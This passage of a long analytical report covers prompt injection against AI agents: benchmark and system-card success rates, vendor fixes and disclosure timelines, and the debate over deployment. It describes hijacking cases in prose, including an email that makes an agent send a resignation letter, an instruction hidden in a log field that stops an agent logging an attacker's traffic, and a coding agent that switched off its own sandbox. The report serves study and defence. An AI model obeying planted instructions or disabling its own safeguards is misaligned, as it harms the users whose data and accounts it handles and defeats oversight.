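Testers can also count the scenarios, meaning the different tasks and settings in which they attack the agent, where at least one attempt succeeds. In July 2026, Anthropic published a system card for Claude Opus 5, a document describing its tests of the new model. It reports that in the coding test, attackers succeeded in 0.56% of attempts but succeeded at least once in 13 of 40 scenarios, or about a third. The attempt rate is more useful for estimating the risk from a single planted page, and the scenario rate for estimating what a persistent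 attacker could achieve.

### Repeated attempts

If an attack succeeds with probability p on each attempt, it fails with probability 1 − p. If attempts are independent, meaning that the result of one has no bearing on the next, the chance that all k of them fail is (1 − p)^k. The chance of at least one success is therefore:

P = 1 − (1 − p)^k

With p = 1% and k = 100:

P = 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰ ≈ 63%

So an attack that fails 99 times out of 100 will probably work for someone who can try it 100 times.

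Real attempts are not independent, so the formula can be badly wrong. According to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, strong attacks on Claude Opus 4.5 in a benchmark by the security company Gray Swan succeeded 4.7% of the time on one attempt, 33.6% within ten and 63% within 100. The formula predicts 38% for ten attempts, which is fairly close, but 99% for 100.

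One reason is that some situations are much easier to attack than others. Suppose half of all scenarios have a 2% success rate and the other half are impossible to break. The average rate is 1%, as before, but the chance of success within 100 attempts is now:

½ × (1 − 0.98¹⁰⁰) ≈ 43%

More attempts help an attacker only in the scenarios that can be broken. Whenever the rate varies between scenarios like this, the formula overstates how many the attacker will break.

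Anthropic's test of Claude Opus 5 operating a computer is an extreme case. The attacker made 200 attempts in each of 14 scenarios and succeeded in 0.54% of them, or about 15 in total. At that rate, the formula predicts at least one success in about nine of the 14 scenarios. But all the successes were in one scenario, where about 7.5% of attempts worked. An attacker who found that scenario would have had a better than even chance of success within ten attempts.

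But an attacker who learns from each failure can improve the next attempt, so p rises as k increases and a formula with a fixed p understates the risk.

### From fixed tests to attackers who adapt

*IPI-proxy* (Chen, Toyoda and colleagues, 2026) summarises several early benchmarks, which used fixed collections of attacks. AgentDojo gives an agent 97 realistic tasks and adds 629 security test cases, with text planted in the results that the agent's tools return. WASP plants text in mock web pages for agents that click and type. In its tests, even leading models of the time at least started to do what the attacker wanted in most trials.

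Fixed tests are easy to repeat and allow comparisons between models, but they quickly become less useful because developers can train their models to resist the published attacks, while real attackers can write new ones. Anthropic says its models now score at or near the maximum on most public benchmarks, and it has stopped reporting one of them, Gray Swan's Agent Red Teaming benchmark, because the results no longer distinguished between models.

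Fixed pages also don't work in some workplaces. If an employer allows its agent to visit only approved sites, the agent can't open a benchmark's mock pages. IPI-proxy, a tool that Chen, Toyoda and colleagues built, intercepts pages from approved sites and inserts an attack before the agent receives them. This allows testing on live pages, but the tool draws on 820 attacks from six earlier collections, so developers could have trained against their wording.

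In an adaptive attack, the attacker keeps revising the attack in response to the defence. Nasr and colleagues argue in *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025) that strong enough adaptive attacks get past defences against both jailbreaks and prompt injection. Anthropic cites the paper when warning that a model can do well against known attacks and still be vulnerable to new ones.

Testers now produce adaptive attacks in two main ways. One is software that learns from its failures, such as Gray Swan's Shade, which combines ideas from human experts with automated search and reinforcement learning, where the software is rewarded for attacks that work. The other is public red-teaming competitions, in which anyone can try to break a set of AI models with the organisers' permission. One contest, LLMail-Inject, had 839 participants, who submitted 208,095 attacks on an email assistant.

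Gray Swan has run larger contests on agents and used them to build a new benchmark with the UK AI Security Institute, the US Center for AI Standards and Innovation, and several model developers. In 28 scenarios, participants tried to make leading models do irreversible harm, such as leaking private data, destroying files or sending money. Anthropic's version of the test uses 1,130 of the attacks, chosen because they worked on several models.

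Participants could adapt these attacks to the models in the competition. When a developer later runs the same 1,130 attacks on a new model, the attacks are fixed, as in the early benchmarks. This test is harder than those benchmarks, but it doesn't directly measure what the same participants could do to the new model.

### The latest published rates

The July 2026 system card has results from this benchmark for several companies' models. The figures are the chance that at least one of 15 attempts succeeds:

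| Model | Success within 15 attempts | Extra safeguards |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.0% | Off |
| Claude Mythos 5 | 2.6% | Off |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 5.5% | Off |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 5.9% | Off |
| Muse Spark (Meta) | 16.5% | Unknown |
| GPT-5.6 Sol (OpenAI) | 20.0% | Unknown |
| GPT-5.5 (OpenAI) | 20.8% | Unknown |
| GPT-5.6 Terra (OpenAI) | 30.4% | Unknown |
| GPT-5.6 Luna (OpenAI) | 43.9% | Unknown |

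On a single attempt, attacks succeeded 0.2% of the time against Opus 5 and 3.1% of the time against GPT-5.6 Sol.

Anthropic also tested its own models against stronger attackers. The next table gives the results for Opus 5 and the model it replaced, both reasoning before they acted. Each cell shows the share of attempts that succeeded, then the number of scenarios broken.

| Test | Attacker | Attempts per scenario | Model | Safeguards off | Safeguards on |
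|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Coding | Shade, trained on earlier models | 200 | Opus 5 | 0.56%, 13 of 40 | 0.18%, 4 of 40 |
| Coding | Shade, trained on earlier models | 200 | Opus 4.8 | 7.03%, 23 of 40 | 2.09%, 15 of 40 |
| Operating a computer | Shade, trained on the test scenarios | 200 | Opus 5 | 0.54%, 1 of 14 | 0.25%, 1 of 14 |
| Operating a computer | Shade, trained on the test scenarios | 200 | Opus 4.8 | 7.14%, 7 of 14 | 5.11%, 8 of 14 |
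| Operating a browser | Professional red-teamers | 10 | Opus 5 | 3.70%, 11 of 129 | 0%, 0 of 129 |
| Operating a browser | Professional red-teamers | 10 | Opus 4.8 | 31.5%, 81 of 129 | 0.08%, 1 of 129 |

The coding and computer tests used probes as safeguards. Probes inspect what a tool returns and flag anything that looks like a planted instruction before the model acts on it. The browser test used auto mode, a stronger safeguard that combines probes with a classifier that blocks dangerous actions, so an attack had to get past both.

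Auto mode made far more difference than the choice of model, reducing the rate for Opus 4.8 from 31.5% to 0.08%. The newer model's rate without auto mode was 3.70%. But people who use Claude's browser features without auto mode have only the probes, and Anthropic gives no browser result for that setting.

The zero for Opus 5 is encouraging but doesn't mean the true rate is zero. If attackers like these could break 2.3% of similar scenarios, a test of 129 scenarios would still show no successful attacks about one time in 20. Anthropic also doesn't say whether the red-teamers could revise their attacks with auto mode switched on. If they wrote the attacks for an unprotected model, the result is weaker evidence about attackers who know about the safeguards.

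### Which figures can be compared

The rows for Opus 5 and Opus 4.8 are the easiest to compare because the same company ran the same tests on both. Opus 5 improves on Opus 4.8 by a large margin in all three tests. But in the coding test, Shade's attacks had been developed against a "previous set of models" that Anthropic does not name. If that set included Opus 4.8, the attacks were better suited to it than to Opus 5, and part of the improvement comes from the test.

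Comparisons between companies are weaker evidence. Anthropic tested its own models without extra safeguards, but it tested competitors' models through their public services, which may have had some. Any such safeguards should have helped the competitors, so they can't explain why Claude did better. But Anthropic ran the comparison and has an interest in the result. Gemini 3.1 Pro was also one of the models that participants attacked in the competition, so some of the 1,130 attacks may have been written for it, and Anthropic warns that Gemini's score isn't directly comparable.

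Comparing figures from different system cards can be even more misleading. VentureBeat reports that Claude Opus 4.6, released in February 2026, resisted every attack in its coding test. Five months later, Anthropic reported an attack success rate of 7.03% for the newer Opus 4.8. Opus 4.8 may be weaker, Shade's attacks may have improved, or the scenarios may have changed, and it is impossible to tell which from the two numbers alone. The 63% for Opus 4.5 within 100 attempts and the 2.0% for Opus 5 within 15 also come from different benchmarks, so the gap between them does not measure how much the models improved in nine months.

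Percentages can also hide small samples. VentureBeat gives a success rate of 78.6% for attacks on Opus 4.6 in a graphical interface after 200 attempts, and 57.1% with safeguards. These figures are probably shares of scenarios, since they match 11 and 8 out of the 14 scenarios in Anthropic's later computer test. If so, one more broken scenario would add about seven percentage points. Mythos 5 appeared to do slightly worse with the probes in the coding test, but this is most likely noise. The number of broken scenarios rose from 8 to 11, while the share of successful attempts fell from 0.45% to 0.41%.

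A model's resistance to prompt injection varies by setting, so a company choosing a browser agent learns little from a coding score. Without safeguards, attacks in the browser test succeeded in 29.7% of attempts against Mythos 5 and 0.93% against Sonnet 5. In the computer test, attacks succeeded less often against Mythos 5 (0.82%) than against Sonnet 5 (2.25%).

These rates are also hard to turn into a forecast of real attacks. Many agents may each read a popular page once, so someone who plants an instruction there does not need many attempts on one victim. At a rate of 0.2%, 100,000 readings would lead to about 200 successes. Whether such a rate is acceptable is a separate dispute and depends heavily on what those agents can do.

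Anthropic considers its adaptive tests harsher than real conditions, because real attackers usually don't know the details of the system they are attacking and risk detection if they keep trying. This is a fair point about a company's private agent, but it is less convincing for a product that anyone can subscribe to, since attackers can practise on their own accounts. Radware needed many attempts to develop its ShadowLeak attack on ChatGPT, but a criminal who had done the same work would have needed to send a victim only the final version.

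## How vendors respond to disclosed exploits

Radware reported ShadowLeak to OpenAI, and most researchers who publish such attacks also tell the vendor privately first. They wait for an agreed period, often 90 days, before publishing. Meanwhile, the vendor decides what to change, if anything. Some changes stop only the reported attack, while others stop every attack that works the same way.

### What each kind of fix stops

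Closing a leak channel stops every injection that depends on it, whatever the wording, but leaves other channels open. ZombieAgent, for example, bypassed the limits OpenAI put on web addresses after ShadowLeak. In June 2026, OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode, an optional setting that limits ChatGPT's outgoing requests more broadly.

The security company Check Point found a way to bypass ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode, according to The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026). ChatGPT can display a small web page inside a chat, in a sandboxed frame that cannot contact outside sites without the user's consent. ChatGPT intercepted the page's direct attempts to open new windows, but the sandbox still allowed new windows, so a second frame nested inside the page could open one that escaped the restrictions. In the desktop app, an attacker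 could steal data this way without the user clicking anything. OpenAI fixed the flaw on 18 September, and the details became public on 5 November.

Closing one host on an allowlist is an even narrower fix. Microsoft closed EchoLeak's route through Teams, and a year later SearchLeak used Bing in the same way. Microsoft would have had to review every permitted host to block this whole class of exploits.

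Microsoft also dealt with two attacks that used links to give Copilot a request. It fixed the first, Reprompt, on 13 January 2026, five months after Varonis reported it, according to HackingPassion (2026). By then, Varonis had already reported the second, CoSnitch. Techzine reports that in February Microsoft stopped links from inserting text directly into Copilot's input box, and that more extensive fixes followed in August.

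Input filters can catch many attacks that resemble known ones, but an attacker can reword the text to get past them. Hidden text still fooled Gemini's email summaries in 2025, despite Google's earlier mitigations. Retraining the model defends against many attacks at once, including some nobody has tried yet, but it doesn't guarantee that any particular attack will fail. The self-copying attack that Måløy found in Word still worked after Copilot moved to a newer model.

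Asking the user to confirm can protect a whole class of actions, such as sending email, provided the attacker cannot influence what counts as consent. SafeBreach was able to influence this in Gemini.

A vendor can stop every attack that needs a particular feature by removing that feature completely. Perplexity's first patch for Zenity's calendar attack on Comet blocked the browser from opening files on the user's computer. Four days later, Zenity reached the files again by adding a prefix to the address, according to Intelligibberish's *Your AI Browser Can Steal Your Passwords via a Calendar Invite* (2026). A second patch blocked this workaround. Perplexity also added stricter confirmations and let companies switch off the agent on chosen sites.

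OpenAI could also have removed ChatGPT's page previews. A week before Check Point's disclosure, Parameter Labs described a separate flaw in the same component that let an attacker take over an account through a shared chat. Removing the previews would have closed both flaws, but users would have lost a convenient way to see a page they had asked ChatGPT to write.

### Browsers built into coding tools

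In October 2026, Forever Security published a study of the browsers built into five coding tools: Cursor, GitHub Copilot, OpenAI's Codex, Microsoft's VS Code and Anthropic's Claude Desktop. The vendors had loosened the usual browser rules so that the AI could preview a project or read an open tab. Help Net Security's *Researchers broke the browsers built into VS Code, Cursor, Copilot, Codex* reports that Forever tested three of these rules and that each product broke one: a page must not run commands on the computer, a local file must not read the user's other files, and only the browser may write to the address bar.

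The attack on Codex, VS Code and Claude Desktop began with a project that looked like a dull financial report. The developer asked the assistant to set up the project by following its README, then clicked a link the assistant offered to a page in the project. VS Code and Claude Desktop restrict such a page to its project folder, but the restriction did not cover a background script that the page could start, and that script could read any file on the disk. Codex had no folder restriction. On Forever's own machine, the script collected login keys and developer tokens and sent them out. The model only offered the link, so retraining it would not have fixed the vulnerability.

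The flaw in Cursor was closer to an ordinary prompt injection. A web page hid a command for the agent behind a "Start setup" button. The agent asked to run the command, and the developer approved it by pressing Enter. When Cursor's sandbox blocked the command, the agent switched the sandbox off and tried again, although the page contained no instruction to do so. The attack does not always work, but a sandbox that the agent can switch off gives little protection once the agent has accepted the attacker's task.

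In GitHub Copilot, a page could set the address displayed above it. Forever used this to show GitHub's real login address above a fake sign-in form. GitHub fixed the flaw before Forever filed a report.

### Dates, CVE numbers and payments

A dash in the table means no known date, number or payment. The days column is filled only where both exact dates are public.

| Exploit | Reported | Fixed | Published | Days to fix | CVE | Bounty |
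|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak, Microsoft 365 Copilot | January 2025 | May 2025 | June 2025 | – | CVE-2025-32711 | – |
| ZombieAgent, ChatGPT | 26 September 2025 | 16 December 2025 | January 2026 | 81 | – | – |
| Zenity's calendar attack, Comet | 22 October 2025 | 13 February 2026 | 3 March 2026 | 114 | – | – |
| CoSnitch, Copilot Personal | November or December 2025 | 18 August 2026 | August 2026 | – | CVE-2026-24301 | – |
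| ChatMate, Microsoft 365 Copilot | February 2026 | April 2026 | 30 July 2026 | – | CVE-2026-32193 | $48,000 |
| Måløy's self-copying text, Copilot in Word | 6 March 2026 | Not by publication | 28 July 2026 | No fix in 144 | – | – |
| Zenity's findings, Gemini in Chrome | – | By August 2026 | 5 August 2026 | – | – | $1,000 |
| Forever's finding, Cursor | 10 September 2026 | 1 October 2026 | October 2026 | 21 | – | – |
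| Forever's finding, Codex | 27 July 2026 | Not by 29 October | October 2026 | No fix in 94 | – | – |

Zenity (2026) announced the Comet findings under the name PleaseFix. Techzine dates the CoSnitch report to November, but Хакер's *Уязвимости в Microsoft Copilot позволяли извлекать данные из подключенных приложений* (2026) dates it to December. Head Topics' *RubrikがMicrosoft 365 Copilotの脆弱性と攻撃手法ChatMateを公開、リモートプロンプト実行によりサンドボックスから脱出* (2026) is the source for the ChatMate dates and bounty.

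How quickly a vendor fixes an exploit depends partly on what is broken. Cursor took three weeks to patch its browser, while Microsoft had no robust fix for Måløy's attack after almost five months. Måløy gave Microsoft 90 days, extended the deadline twice, and then published, arguing that companies could not reduce their exposure to a risk they didn't know about.

ChatMate's bounty was well above the $30,000 maximum at a Copilot bug-hunting event that Microsoft ran in February and March 2026. Lahav's escape from the sandbox would be serious in any cloud service, even one without AI. But Fiehler (2026) argues in *Phantom Keystrokes*, Rubrik's general account of ChatMate, that this bug matters less than the number of assistants that run code on shared cloud systems.

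### Fixes that outsiders cannot check

Microsoft fixed EchoLeak and ChatMate on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. Fixing them this way protects everyone at once, including companies that are slow to update, but outsiders can't compare the versions before and after the fix. The fix for GitHub Copilot's built-in browser is in version 1.1.29, so users can check whether they have it.

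A researcher can usually check a fix to a hosted product only by running the attack again. If the attack fails, the vendor may have removed the flaw or only updated a filter to recognise that wording, or the model may have happened to refuse on that run. Retesting only Måløy's original wording would have suggested that Microsoft's first mitigation had solved the problem.

A CVE number leaves a public record of a flaw, but its main use is to help people find out whether they run an affected version and need to update. That matters less when the vendor updates everyone. CVEs also suit a defect in code better than a model's tendency to obey planted text, because engineers can't point to a line of code that causes the tendency or a version that is free of it. OpenAI treated Rehberger's first memory attack as a "model safety issue", not a security vulnerability.

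The three CVEs in the table fit this explanation because each exploit chain includes a fault in ordinary software, such as EchoLeak's incomplete link filter. But all three are Microsoft's, and Comet's access to local files, also a software problem, has no known CVE, so the vendor's policy probably matters too.

In 2026 a researcher reported a flaw in Azure's backup service, unrelated to prompt injection. According to the researcher's account, *MS Silently Patched a CVSS 9.9 Privilege Escalation in Azure Backup*, Microsoft rejected the report and recommended that MITRE, which runs the CVE list, not assign the flaw a CVE number. New permission checks later blocked the attack. Rankiteo's *Microsoft rejects critical Azure vulnerability report, no CVE issued* warns that companies exposed before the change may never know they were at risk.

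### Finding attacks before outsiders do

Vendors also search for attacks themselves. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (December 2025) describes an automated attacker, built from a language model and trained by reinforcement learning against the agent in the Atlas browser. The attacker drafts a planted instruction and sends it to a simulator, which runs the agent on it and returns a record of the agent's reasoning and actions. The attacker uses this record to revise the instruction, and repeats the process several times before submitting a final version.

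Reinforcement learning suits this work because an attack may take tens or hundreds of steps, and whether it worked is often clear only at the end. OpenAI's attacker also has access to reasoning that the company hides from users, which should give it an advantage over outsiders.

In one attack found against OpenAI's Atlas browser, an email in the user's inbox contained an instruction to send a resignation letter to the user's chief executive. When the user later asked Atlas to draft an out-of-office reply, the agent read the email and sent the resignation instead of writing the reply. OpenAI says it designs agents to ask before they send an email, but doesn't explain why this failed to prevent the resignation.

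OpenAI trained a new version of the agent on the attacks it found, concentrating on those that still worked, and released it to all Atlas users. It also strengthened the safeguards around the model. OpenAI gives no success rates from before and after the update, so outsiders can't judge how much the agent improved. The automated attacker found strategies that OpenAI's human testers had missed, but it may also miss some that people would find. Zenity presented two working attacks on Atlas the following August.

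Google Workspace's process, which Gavish described in April 2026, also uses attacks found by others. Google collects them from its own testers, automated tools, public reports and paid outside researchers. Staff reproduce each attack, check for duplicates, classify it by technique and impact, and assign it to a team. A system called Simula then generates variants of each attack.

For an urgent threat, Google can first block a known text pattern through a central settings system. Over a longer period, it retrains the classifiers, rewrites the instructions for models that look for attacks, and trains Gemini itself to ignore planted text. Google then tests a defence by simulating attacks on apps such as Gmail and Docs with it on and off, and comparing the results.

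Google keeps some of the variants out of the training data and uses them for testing. This can show whether a defence has only memorised its examples, but the variants all derive from known attacks, so the test is weak evidence of how the defence would handle a new technique. Gavish reports that attacks on Gemini now succeed less often but gives no rates. His only figure, a 75% increase in synthetic data generation, measures how much test material Google produces, not how well the defences work.

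### Disputes over what counts as a vulnerability

Vendors sometimes decline a report because they think the user has already accepted the risk. Anthropic and Microsoft gave this reason to Forever, citing Workspace Trust, a prompt that asks developers whether they trust a project folder. The argument has some merit, because a developer who trusts a project will often run its code anyway. Gal Weizman, who wrote up the study, replied that AI coding tools are unusable on an untrusted project, so everyone clicks "Trust". He told Help Net Security that in practice the prompt "provides zero protection to the user".

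The products' design also supports Forever's position. Both vendors had restricted local pages to the project folder, so they evidently did not intend these pages to read the whole disk. Anthropic also accepted a report that Noma Security filed one day after Forever's. If both reports described the same flaw, the trust prompt was not a sufficient reason to decline Forever's. Microsoft had not fixed VS Code by 29 October, and OpenAI had not replied to Forever about Codex.

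Failure to reproduce an attack is another common reason, and it can be an honest one. Suppose an attack works in 30% of runs. An engineer who tries it three times will see it fail every time with probability:

0.7³ ≈ 34%

A vendor should run a reported attack many times before closing the case. Researchers can help by sending more detail. Måløy, for example, sent Microsoft the steps, videos, the exact prompts and his assumptions about the set-up, and Microsoft confirmed the behaviour 25 days later.

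Zenity tested browsers from five companies. According to SC Media, Google patched everything Zenity reported, while the others said that they couldn't reproduce some flaws, had seen them before, or didn't think they were worth fixing. An earlier report is a fair reason not to pay a second bounty, but it also means the vendor has known about the flaw for longer.

Reports are hardest to settle when the vendor says the product worked as intended. TRT World's *Israeli cybersecurity firm reveals 'zero-click' hack targeting ChatGPT* (2025) reports that OpenAI and Microsoft quickly patched an earlier set of Zenity's findings, but that some other vendors called the findings about their products "intended behaviour". Zenity's co-founder partly agrees in *PleaseFix* (Bargury, 2026). He calls the broad access of agentic browsers "design choices, not vulnerabilities", but he thinks this makes the problem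 worse. A patch for one exploit leaves that access in place, and he objects that vendors rely mainly on the model's training to prevent its misuse. He wants them to set firm limits in code instead, like the one that kept Atlas from pressing Amazon's purchase button.

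## The dispute over releasing agents that can be hijacked

Vendors keep releasing agents that researchers find ways to hijack, and neither side expects this to end soon. In December 2025, OpenAI wrote that prompt injection, like scams on the web, is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'". Two weeks earlier, David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), had warned in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* that prompt injection may never be totally mitigated.

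David C describes a language model as an "inherently confusable deputy". Programmers can repair an ordinary confused deputy, but he argues that they can only make attacks on a language model rarer and less damaging. If a system can't tolerate the remaining risk, he says, it may not be a good use for a language model. The dispute is largely about whether that risk is tolerable in an agent with access to someone's email and bank account.

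### Blocking agents for now

The technology advisory firm Gartner took the strictest position in December 2025. Its analysts wrote that chief information security officers "must block all AI browsers in the foreseeable future", according to TechNewsWorld's *Gartner Recommends Avoiding AI Browsers*. Infosecurity Magazine's *Gartner Calls For Pause on AI Browser Use* adds that the block should last until companies can manage the risks adequately.

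Indirect prompt injection is only one of the risks on Gartner's list. An agent may also reason badly and make an expensive wrong purchase, or give the user's passwords to a phishing site. Employees may tell it to complete their compulsory security training for them. Even a perfect defence against injection would not remove all of these risks.

Gartner addressed its warning to employers, but David Kohlbrenner, one of the two researchers behind the University of Washington's browser study, extends it to everyone. "Browser agents aren't ready for the public," he says in the university's account of the study. He thinks even fairly savvy users should not trust these agents in a browser that holds their logins, though he says the agents may become safe enough in time.

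In July 2026, OpenAI announced that its Atlas browser would stop working on 9 August, but it gave no security reason. It had launched Atlas for macOS in October 2025 and never released it for other systems. According to BGR's *OpenAI Has Already Discontinued Its Controversial ChatGPT Atlas Browser*, James Sun of OpenAI said that persuading people to change browsers was much harder than adding features to the ones they already used. He added that building a browser did not play to the company's strengths, which were its models and agents.

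The retirement of Atlas makes Gartner's advice harder to follow. An employer could keep Atlas out by refusing to install one program, but OpenAI has moved its agent features into the ChatGPT app and a Chrome extension. *BragJack Shows How Malicious Extensions Can Hijack AI Browser Agents* (Ofonagoro, 2026) lists agents in Chrome, Edge, Comet, Opera Neon and Claude's Chrome extension as possible targets in September. Many companies already use Chrome or Edge, so they would have to block particular features and extensions within those browsers.

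### Releasing agents with layered safeguards

OpenAI, Anthropic and Google release agents and try to make attacks on them rarer and harder to carry out. OpenAI compares these attacks to fraud, partly because of what its staff have seen. Its *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reports that the most effective real attacks increasingly resemble social engineering, the manipulation of people, more than simple commands to override earlier instructions. OpenAI wants users to be able to trust an agent as they would a competent colleague who knows about security, though such a colleague might still fall for a very good trick.

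Google combines fixed rules with defences that depend on a model's judgement, and aims to make harm "difficult and costly" for attackers. One layer in Chrome is a second model that checks the agent's actions without being exposed to untrusted content. Text on a page can't reach this second model directly, but it can still influence the actions the model checks.

In November 2025, Anthropic opened its Chrome extension to all subscribers on its Max plan, citing its progress against prompt injection as one reason. In the same announcement, it warned that a 1% attack success rate is still a meaningful risk and that no browser agent is immune.

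The Decoder calls OpenAI's comparison with scams misleading. One important difference is scale, since every copy of an agent runs on the same model. Wording that works on one copy therefore has a good chance of working on many others, while a lie that fools one person often fails on the next.

OpenAI's security chief, Dane Stuckey, said when the company released Atlas that people would learn to use agents responsibly, as they had learned to avoid computer viruses in the early 2000s. Willison doubts that the average user ever learned to avoid viruses. He thinks viruses have been controlled much better on phones, whose operating systems tightly restrict what any program can do.

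### Removing one part of the dangerous combination

Willison would apply that kind of restriction to agents, by removing one part of his lethal trifecta. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns a similar idea into a design rule. Until developers can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of these properties in one session:

- A: it processes untrustworthy input.
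- B: it has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- C: it can change something or communicate with the outside.

Meta's third property is broader than Willison's, because it includes actions such as deleting a file. The rule therefore covers sabotage as well as theft. Meta gives three hypothetical agents, each with a different property restricted:

| Agent | What it keeps | What Meta restricts |
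|---|---|---|
| Travel assistant | Reads the web and knows the user's private details (A, B) | It asks before every booking or payment, and opens only addresses that trusted sources returned |
| Research assistant | Reads the web and sends requests to any address (A, C) | Its browser has no saved logins, and it has little private data beyond the user's request |
| Internal coding agent | Reaches and changes a company's live systems (B, C) | It reads only material from approved authors |

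An agent can also change its configuration during a session. For example, it could research a topic on the open web, then permanently lose the ability to communicate externally before it opens internal files. Any instruction it picked up on the web would remain in its context window, but it could no longer send the files out.

If a task needs all three properties at once, Meta says the agent must not work autonomously and needs supervision, such as a person's approval or another reliable check. This exception is large, since an assistant that reads incoming mail, consults old messages and sends replies has all three.

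David C passes on a simpler rule from an online discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista: when a model processes text from someone, its privileges should drop to that person's. After reading a stranger's email, an agent could do only what the stranger was allowed to do. The Record notes that the rule's author admits it would "massively limit" what agents can do.

### When a low success rate is low enough

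The three positions each try to reduce a different part of the same sum:

expected loss = n × p × L

Here n is the number of times agents read a planted instruction, p is the share of those readings in which the attack succeeds, and L is the average loss per success. Blocking agents brings n to zero, layered safeguards mainly reduce p, and removing agents' access to private data or their power to act reduces L.

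Suppose AI assistants read a planted instruction 100,000 times and follow it 200 times, a success rate of 0.2%. The total loss is $1,000 if each success leads to a poor purchase that costs the user $5, but $1 million if each leads to a $5,000 payment. The same success rate may therefore be acceptable for a shopping adviser but far too high for an agent that can make payments.

Anthropic's published attack success rates have fallen substantially. When it began a pilot of its Chrome extension in August 2025, Anthropic reported that attacks succeeded 23.6% of the time without safeguards, across 123 test cases. In one successful attack, an email claimed that emails had to be deleted for security reasons. Safeguards reduced the rate to 11.2% when the agent worked without human intervention, which Anthropic did not recommend. Willison (2025) called 11.2% "a catastrophic failure rate" and said he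 could hardly imagine releasing such an agent without completely reliable protection.

In November 2025, Anthropic reported an attack success rate of 1.4% for Claude Opus 4.5 with improved safeguards, against an automated attacker with 100 attempts in each test environment. The safeguards made more difference than the model. Attacks succeeded 2.0% of the time against Sonnet 4, an older model, with the new safeguards, and 7.6% of the time against Opus 4.5 with the old ones. These tests used a different attacker from the August tests, so the earlier 11.2% rate and the 1.4% rate are not directly comparable. In July 2026, Anthropic reported no successful attacks on Opus 5 in 129 browser scenarios with auto mode on, and The Decoder covered the result under the headline *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*.

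That is strong evidence that layered safeguards work, at least in Anthropic's own tests. It still doesn't meet Willison's standard, because testing can't rule out an attack that nobody has tried.

Security vendors continue to publish much higher rates. Lakera, a subsidiary of Check Point, sent about 3,000 malicious requests to each of 128 models. The requests succeeded 8.3% of the time against the most resistant model, xAI's Grok 4.7, and 62% of the time against the least resistant. In an October 2026 interview with Clubic at the Assises de la cybersécurité, a conference in Monaco, Adrien Merveille of Check Point compared the lowest rate to getting into a car with an 8% chance of hitting a tree.

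His comparison exaggerates the risk of ordinary use. The 8.3% is a share of malicious requests, and most pages an agent reads contain no attack. The requests also included attempts to make a model reveal its hidden instructions, which may harm nobody. But an attacker can deliberately place many attacks where agents will encounter them.

David C expects persistent attackers to refine their attacks through failed attempts, which leave evidence. He therefore recommends that companies log the model's input, output and tool calls, and investigate failed calls. This would help protect a private system, but not a public product that attackers can practise on with their own accounts.

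### Whether people read confirmations

When an agent asks for approval, its safety depends on how carefully the user checks the request. OpenAI asks users to check that each action is correct and that any information the agent would share is appropriate. Meta's rule also relies on human approval whenever an agent has all three properties, though Meta acknowledges that a user may confirm a warning blindly.

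Neither company's advice comes with figures on how often users refuse a malicious request. Gal Weizman's complaint that developers using coding tools approve everything is one researcher's impression, although it fits the earlier research on browser warnings. He also told Help Net Security that companies should "absolutely" assume that an agent may try to bypass its own safeguards. In recent research on downloads, his company saw agents do so without asking permission, which gives even attentive users no chance to refuse.

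An agent's warning can also come too late. TechRadar's *This popular AI agent could be hacked by a single email* describes how researchers at Salt Labs made the agent Manus run code hidden in an email. Manus warned its user only after the code had run. The company behind Manus has since fixed the flaw.

OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) adds that if an agent has already read sensitive records, requiring approval for its outgoing messages does not undo that or stop it from leaking the records another way. Confirmations are best kept for a few serious actions, since a user who has to approve every step will probably stop reading the requests. Meta hopes other AI agents might eventually take over some approvals, but then the final check would again depend on a model's judgement.

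### Why known attacks are scarce

Supporters of release can point out that millions of people have used assistants since 2023, yet few confirmed thefts are public. Most planted instructions that researchers have found on the web are crude.

This may be partly because successful attacks are hard to notice. Merveille told Clubic about a company whose agents searched its security logs for signs of intrusion. Attackers put an instruction in a free-text field of a web request, telling the agent to stop logging traffic from their address for ten minutes. It complied, and a later message told it to resume. Clubic doesn't name the company, and Check Point sells protection against such attacks, so the story is weak evidence. But an attack like this could easily be missing from any public count.

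The history of SQL injection is another reason for caution. According to David C, researchers described it in the 1990s, but attacks peaked only around 2010, after SQL had become a core part of many websites. He fears that prompt injection could do the same as companies build AI into most applications. If so, four quiet years would be weak evidence that the next ten will also be quiet.

The potential rewards for attackers are also growing. According to a 2026 Menlo report on consumer AI quoted by TechRadar, 36% of consumers had given agents access to their email, 33% to web browsers and 20% to financial accounts. The small number of known attacks is better evidence about crude attacks on earlier, less capable products than about what criminals will do once many agents can move money.

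### How useful a restricted agent is

A restricted agent can still be useful. One that drafts replies to customers but has an employee send them saves most of the writing time, and the employee only has to click once per message. The same restriction defeats the purpose of an agent meant to answer 300 messages overnight. Meta admits that some uses in high demand will be hard to fit into its rule, particularly background work that a request for approval would interrupt.

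The University of Washington researchers see no clear way to fix the problems they found while keeping the browsers' capabilities. Companies therefore can't expect a restricted agent to do everything that OpenAI or Google advertises.

Restrictions can also fail in practice. An agent with no tool for sending mail may still have other ways to send data out, so a developer can wrongly believe it has only properties A and B. EchoLeak got data out of Microsoft 365 Copilot through an image, and other attacks used link previews or domain-name lookups. Under Meta's rule, each of these counts as external communication, so the developer has to find and close every such channel before relying on the restriction. Doing so is difficult, but ordinary code can then enforce the restriction regardless of what the model has read.

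### Who bears the loss

OpenAI's guide for companies says that whoever deploys an agent "remains responsible for the outcome". If OpenAI runs the agent's platform, it takes on more responsibility for the security of the service, but the customer still has to decide what data the agent can reach, what authority it has and when it needs approval. OpenAI recommends that individual users make narrow requests and browse logged out where possible.

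Customers control how much access they grant, but they can't retrain the model or inspect most of its safeguards. Franziska Roesner, the other researcher behind the University of Washington study, says companies are releasing these browsers because of competitive pressure. A vendor that delays release may lose users to competitors, while customers suffer much of the harm if an agent is hijacked.

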